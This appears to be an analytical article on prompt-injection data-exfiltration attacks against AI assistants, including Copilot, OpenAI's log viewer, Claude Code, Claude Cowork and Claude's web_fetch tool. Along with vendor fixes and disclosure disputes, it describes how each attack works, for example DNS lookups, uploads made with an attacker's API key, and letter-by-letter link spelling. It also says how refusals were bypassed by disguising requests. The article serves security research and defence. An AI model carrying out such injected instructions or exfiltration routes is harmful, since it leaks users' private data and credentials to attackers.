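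The Hacker News is right. The change history in *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), a vulnerability tracker's page with the same title as Microsoft's, shows that NVD added its own score of 7.5 on 8 June. That score differs from Microsoft's 6.5 only because NVD assumed that the victim does not have to do anything. SearchLeak starts with a click on a link, so Microsoft's score fits the published attack better. EchoLeak, which needed no click, scored 9.3.

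Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak before publishing the record and knew of no attacks that used it.

### Why the leak keeps returning

Ready-made Markdown software displays images by default, so anyone who builds a new app, preview page or internal tool has to know about the leak and add protection again. On his blog Embrace The Red, Rehberger says he expects this to remain a problem even at OpenAI, which has a good check that some developers may not know to use.

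PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes a data leak in the log viewer, where developers who build on OpenAI's models review past conversations. In the demonstration, a bank's assistant checks a customer's identity using private records and material from the web. The web material contains a prompt injection that makes the model write an image address containing the customer's details. A safeguard in the bank's app blocks the answer and flags it for review. When a developer opens the conversation in the log viewer, the viewer displays the image, which sends the details to the attacker.

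The bank had followed security advice, but the review of the blocked attack allowed the attack to succeed. PromptArmor reported the problem on 17 November 2025. Bugcrowd, which screened such reports for OpenAI, closed it as "Not applicable" on 4 December. OpenAI saw the report only after PromptArmor published its article. It reopened the report on 22 January 2026, six days before it publicly explained its new address check. PromptArmor found the same flaw in sample software that OpenAI gives developers as a starting point, so developers could copy it into products OpenAI never sees.

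Unprotected clients would be harmless if models always ignored injected instructions, but no known method guarantees that. What Willison calls the lethal trifecta combines private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out. The first two are the hardest to remove, because people connect an assistant to their email so that it can use private data, and email consists largely of text from other people. Vendors have therefore usually fixed the flaw by restricting how data can be sent out.

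Vendors have not always accepted that they had a flaw to fix. OpenAI first called the images a feature and later classed planted memories as a safety issue. Willison reports that in November 2025, Google's page for outside researchers listed data exfiltration through prompt injection in Antigravity as a "known issue". Google said it was working on a fix but would not pay for reports of the problem. A company has little reason to pay for the same discovery twice, and admitting the flaw is better than denying it. But Antigravity was available to users before the flaw was fixed, and researchers had less reason to look for new versions of it.

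OpenAI's objection to strict allowlists is a stronger argument for the vendors. A chatbot that answers questions about an uploaded file loses almost nothing if it cannot contact outside servers. An assistant built to browse the web has to contact them, so its developers must decide which requests are safe, and they will get some of those decisions wrong.

Users can also reopen a route for data leaks after a vendor has closed it. The Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting AI models to other software, lets people combine tools from different companies. One tool might read private files, another fetch web pages, and a third send messages. Each can be safe on its own, but Willison warns that no vendor can protect a user who combines them.

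## 2024 to 2026: later data leaks from Claude

Anthropic's 2023 fix covered only Claude's website, so the iPhone app needed a separate fix, which Rehberger announced in December 2024. In the announcement, quoted in Willison (2024), he says phone apps often have this flaw too.

The model writes the same Markdown for every client, but each client uses its own code to turn it into images. ChatGPT's apps had lacked protection for the same reason. A company could protect all its clients by removing image addresses on its servers before sending any of the answer.

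By April 2026 claude.ai had apparently stopped showing outside images in its answers. The evidence is a complaint by the developer dzhurinskiy, *Image content blocks from tool results not rendered inline in assistant response* (issue 1329 on the public page for Anthropic's Python software kit). It describes a tool that draws charts for Claude. Claude could see and correctly describe a chart, but users had to open a collapsed panel to see it. The developer tried having the tool return the chart's web address instead, and found that claude.ai does not display external images inline.

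This is one developer's observation, and it covers only the website. It does show that blocking images takes more away from users than it did in 2023, when Claude had no tools that could draw a chart. Claude can also now send data out without an image, because Anthropic has since given it tools that run commands, execute programs and open web pages, each of which can contact a server.

### Domain lookups from Claude Code

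Claude Code, Anthropic's programming assistant, runs on the developer's computer. It can read a project's files without asking but needs permission to run most commands. Embrace The Red's *Claude Code* describes how Rehberger found a list in the program's code of commands that could run without approval because they seemed harmless. He asked Claude to look for weaknesses in the list, and it picked out four commands that look up internet addresses.

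Such lookups use the Domain Name System (DNS), which translates names like example.com into the numeric addresses computers use to reach each other. A query for any name ending in example.com contains the full name and normally reaches a server chosen by the domain's owner. If a hijacked assistant looks up "secret.example.com", the owner can read "secret" in the server's log. The name doesn't have to exist, and no web page or image has to load.

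In Rehberger's demonstration, text planted in a source file made Claude Code read an access key from a settings file and send it out in a lookup. Such a key can let an attacker use the developer's paid services or reach customer data. Claude refused when he asked for this directly, so he disguised the request. It also refused to contact domains known for security testing, but accepted an ordinary domain that he owned. Claude seems to have based its refusals more on familiar warning signs than on what the command would do.

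Rehberger reported the flaw on 26 May 2025. Anthropic rated it 7.1 out of 10 (high severity) and told him on 6 June that the flaw was fixed. The public catalogue of software flaws lists it as CVE-2025-55284. Rehberger had suggested taking the four commands off the list, so that developers would have to approve them.

Anthropic later found that user approval is a weak safeguard. Its *How we contain Claude across products*, published in May 2026, reports that users accepted about 93% of Claude Code's permission requests and paid less attention the more requests they saw. Most of those requests were presumably harmless, so users would not necessarily approve 93% of attacks, but the finding is still evidence against relying on the "Show Image" button. Anthropic has since added a sandbox to Claude Code, a closed-off environment that blocks network access by default. This also cut permission requests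 by 84%.

### Uploads to the attacker's Anthropic account

In 2025 Anthropic gave the Claude chat app a sandbox on Anthropic's servers where Claude can write and run programs. Those programs often have to download other software, so the default setting allowed connections to a short list of approved domains. The first entry was api.anthropic.com, which developers use to connect their own software to Claude.

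That address also hosts a file storage service, the Files API. Each request includes an API key, a long password that determines which account the request belongs to. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how Rehberger used this key in October 2025. A user asks Claude to summarise a document that contains hidden instructions and the attacker's key. Claude saves private data to a file and runs a short program that uploads the file with the attacker's key. The sandbox allows the connection because it goes to Anthropic, and the file arrives in the attacker's account.

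The Einstein file had asked for a 20-word summary of the current conversation. This attack could send 30 megabytes per file, and the demonstration took an earlier conversation, which Claude could look up through a new memory feature. The attack worked on the first try, but Claude then refused the instructions for some time, apparently because a key in plain text looked suspicious. Rehberger got past the refusals by adding harmless code around the request. He proposed that the sandbox let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

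Anthropic rejected the report, then accepted it five days later. In January 2026 it released Claude Cowork, an assistant for office work that can read and change files in a folder on the user's computer. Within two days the security company PromptArmor had used the same upload route against it. In PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, a user connects a folder of property documents and adds a Word file that supposedly teaches Claude about real estate. The file contains instructions in white, one-point type. Cowork then uploads a loan estimate with partial social security numbers to the attacker's account, without asking for approval.

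PromptArmor used Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, for this demonstration. In a second test, Opus 4.5, known to resist injections better, also uploaded customer records. PromptArmor complained that Anthropic had acknowledged Rehberger's finding without fixing it. TechNadu reported in *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* that Anthropic acknowledged the risk and was updating the virtual machine, a simulated computer, in which Cowork runs programs.

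The route was still open in the ordinary chat app when the security company Oasis investigated it. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes an attack that starts with a Google advertisement showing a genuine claude.com address. That address forwarded visitors to any site named in the link, and the attack used it to open a new Claude chat with a question already filled in. Part of the question was invisible in the text box, but Claude received all of it when the user pressed Enter. The hidden part was an instruction to search the user's past conversations and upload what Claude found.

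Microsoft's SearchLeak also used a link with a prepared question. Attacks through such links are hard for a model to resist because the attacker's text arrives as the user's own message. Anthropic had seen this problem in an internal exercise in February 2026, when one of its researchers tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a malicious prompt. When Anthropic repeated the prompt 25 times, Claude sent out the employee's cloud credentials 24 times. Anthropic's defences inside the model check for departures from what the user wants, and in this case the user appeared to have asked for the credentials to be sent.

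Anthropic had fixed the hidden-text flaw by the time Oasis published its findings on 18 March. Luz's article, last updated on 27 May, still describes the other two flaws as "currently being addressed".

In its May 2026 account, Anthropic describes a fix for Cowork that closely resembles Rehberger's proposal. A program inside the virtual machine now checks all traffic to Anthropic's API and passes on only requests with the token issued to that session, so it rejects requests with an attacker's key. The check has to happen there because Anthropic's servers cannot distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's. Anthropic describes this fix only for Cowork, so it is unclear whether the chat app, where Rehberger found the leak, has the same protection.

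Anthropic had thought of its allowlist as a list of places Claude could connect to. It now calls each entry a "capability grant", because allowing Claude to reach a domain also allows it to use everything the domain offers. Google and Microsoft had run into the same problem with their allowlists. Anthropic also argues that its model could not have helped stop the attack, since nothing in it looked unusual. Rehberger's experience suggests otherwise, because Claude refused for a while. However, an attacker can keep trying until a version of the attack works.

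### Spelling out a name with links

Claude can also read web pages through the web_fetch tool, which Anthropic released to developers in September 2025. Opening a page sends its address to a server, as loading an image does, so the tool could have allowed the same kind of leak as in 2023 without an image.

Anthropic prevented the simple version by barring Claude from opening addresses it composes itself. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* explains that Claude can open only addresses that the user has provided or that come from earlier searches or fetched pages. If an injected text tells Claude to add a user's travel plans to an example.com address and open it, the tool blocks the request because the combined address has never appeared in the conversation. This works even if the attacker has completely hijacked the model. Willison tested the tool in the consumer app that September and found that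 it blocked this kind of leak. He also warned developers that their software often inserts untrusted text into the user's messages, and that the tool would accept any address in that text.

The weak point turned out to be the links on fetched pages, because whoever owns a website chooses its links. Paul (2026), in *The Memory Heist*, describes a site with one link for each letter of the alphabet. Each link led to a page with another set of letters, which the server generated as needed. If a user is called Anna, Claude can spell the name by opening four pages in turn:

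```
/a
/an
/ann
/anna
```

Each address was a link on the previous page, so every request followed the rule. Claude chose which links to open but did not compose the addresses, and the attacker could read its choices in the server's log. Each request conveyed one character, as in the attack on ChatGPT that Radware had disclosed.

The attack still required Claude to follow the injected instructions, and Paul's first simple injections were unreliable. The version that worked was a coffee shop website with a security check, falsely attributed to the internet company Cloudflare, that asked AI assistants to identify their users. According to *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026), the site showed this check only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. A person who opened the same address would have seen nothing odd.

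Claude leaked Paul's name, home town and employer. Paul did not have to mention any of these in the conversation, because Claude's memory feature adds a summary of past chats to each new one. Unlike in 2023, even a new conversation therefore contained private information.

Anthropic fixed the flaw by stopping web_fetch from following links on pages it had fetched. Claude can now open only addresses that the user has entered or that its search tool has returned. This is somewhat less convenient for users, since Claude can no longer click through to the next page of an article by itself. Claude's choice among search results could in principle still leak some data, but an attacker would first have to get suitable pages into those results and could no longer generate them on demand.

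Paul received no bounty because Anthropic said it had already found the flaw internally. This is plausible, since its documentation had listed links from fetched pages as allowed and warned of "residual risk". If so, Anthropic knew of the gap before Paul's report and had not yet closed it.

### A safety issue or a security flaw

Rehberger reported the Files API leak on 25 October 2025, and Anthropic closed the report within an hour. It considered the leak a model safety issue, which its disclosure policy excluded. The version of the policy that Anthropic replaced in May 2026 gave a separate email address for reporting jailbreaks (prompts that make a model ignore its safety rules).

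There are practical reasons for this division. People keep finding new ways to make a model say something it shouldn't, and engineers usually can't fix each one as they would a faulty line of code. Anthropic had also warned users about this risk in a help page, *Create and edit files with Claude*, which explains that hidden instructions can trick Claude into sending private data to outsiders. The page recommends watching Claude and stopping it if it does something unexpected.

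Rehberger considered the leak a security vulnerability in the default network settings. "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries," he wrote. The default was called "Package managers only", and a user could reasonably assume that it kept private files from reaching strangers. After he published his findings, Anthropic told him that such leaks were reportable after all and that it should not have closed his report. SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration* gives the same sequence of events.

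Rehberger has the better argument. The model made a mistake, but the data could leave only because the sandbox accepted an attacker's key. Anthropic fixed this in Cowork by changing the software around the model. It had already accepted his reports about the Einstein file and Claude Code's DNS lookups as vulnerabilities, although both attacks began with a prompt injection.

The advice to watch Claude is a poor substitute for a fix. In PromptArmor's demonstration, the user could see the upload command only by opening a collapsed block. PromptArmor quotes Willison's objection that it is unfair to expect non-programmers to recognise the signs of prompt injection. Turning off the sandbox's network access works better, but Anthropic leaves that access on by default for individual users. Even with it off, tools connected to Claude can still send data out.

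Anthropic published new bug bounty rules in May 2026. They cover flaws in its infrastructure and code but exclude "model content and responses", such as jailbreaks and hallucinations. The rules don't mention prompt injection, so Anthropic's reviewers must still decide whether a leak like Rehberger's is covered. Products in a research preview also count as less important for their first month. PromptArmor published its attack on Cowork when the product was two days old.

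Anthropic concedes that defences inside the model will never be fully effective. On one outside benchmark, attacks on its Opus 4.7 model succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, but 5–6% when attackers could adapt over 100 attempts. In August 2026, Rehberger's *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (wunderwuzzi, 2026) reported an attack success rate of 60–80% in a small targeted test of Claude Code, compared with 0.00% in an evaluation commissioned by Anthropic. *Claude Code can be hijacked by a web page* (Constantin, 2026) reports that Anthropic told Rehberger that Claude Code was working as designed.
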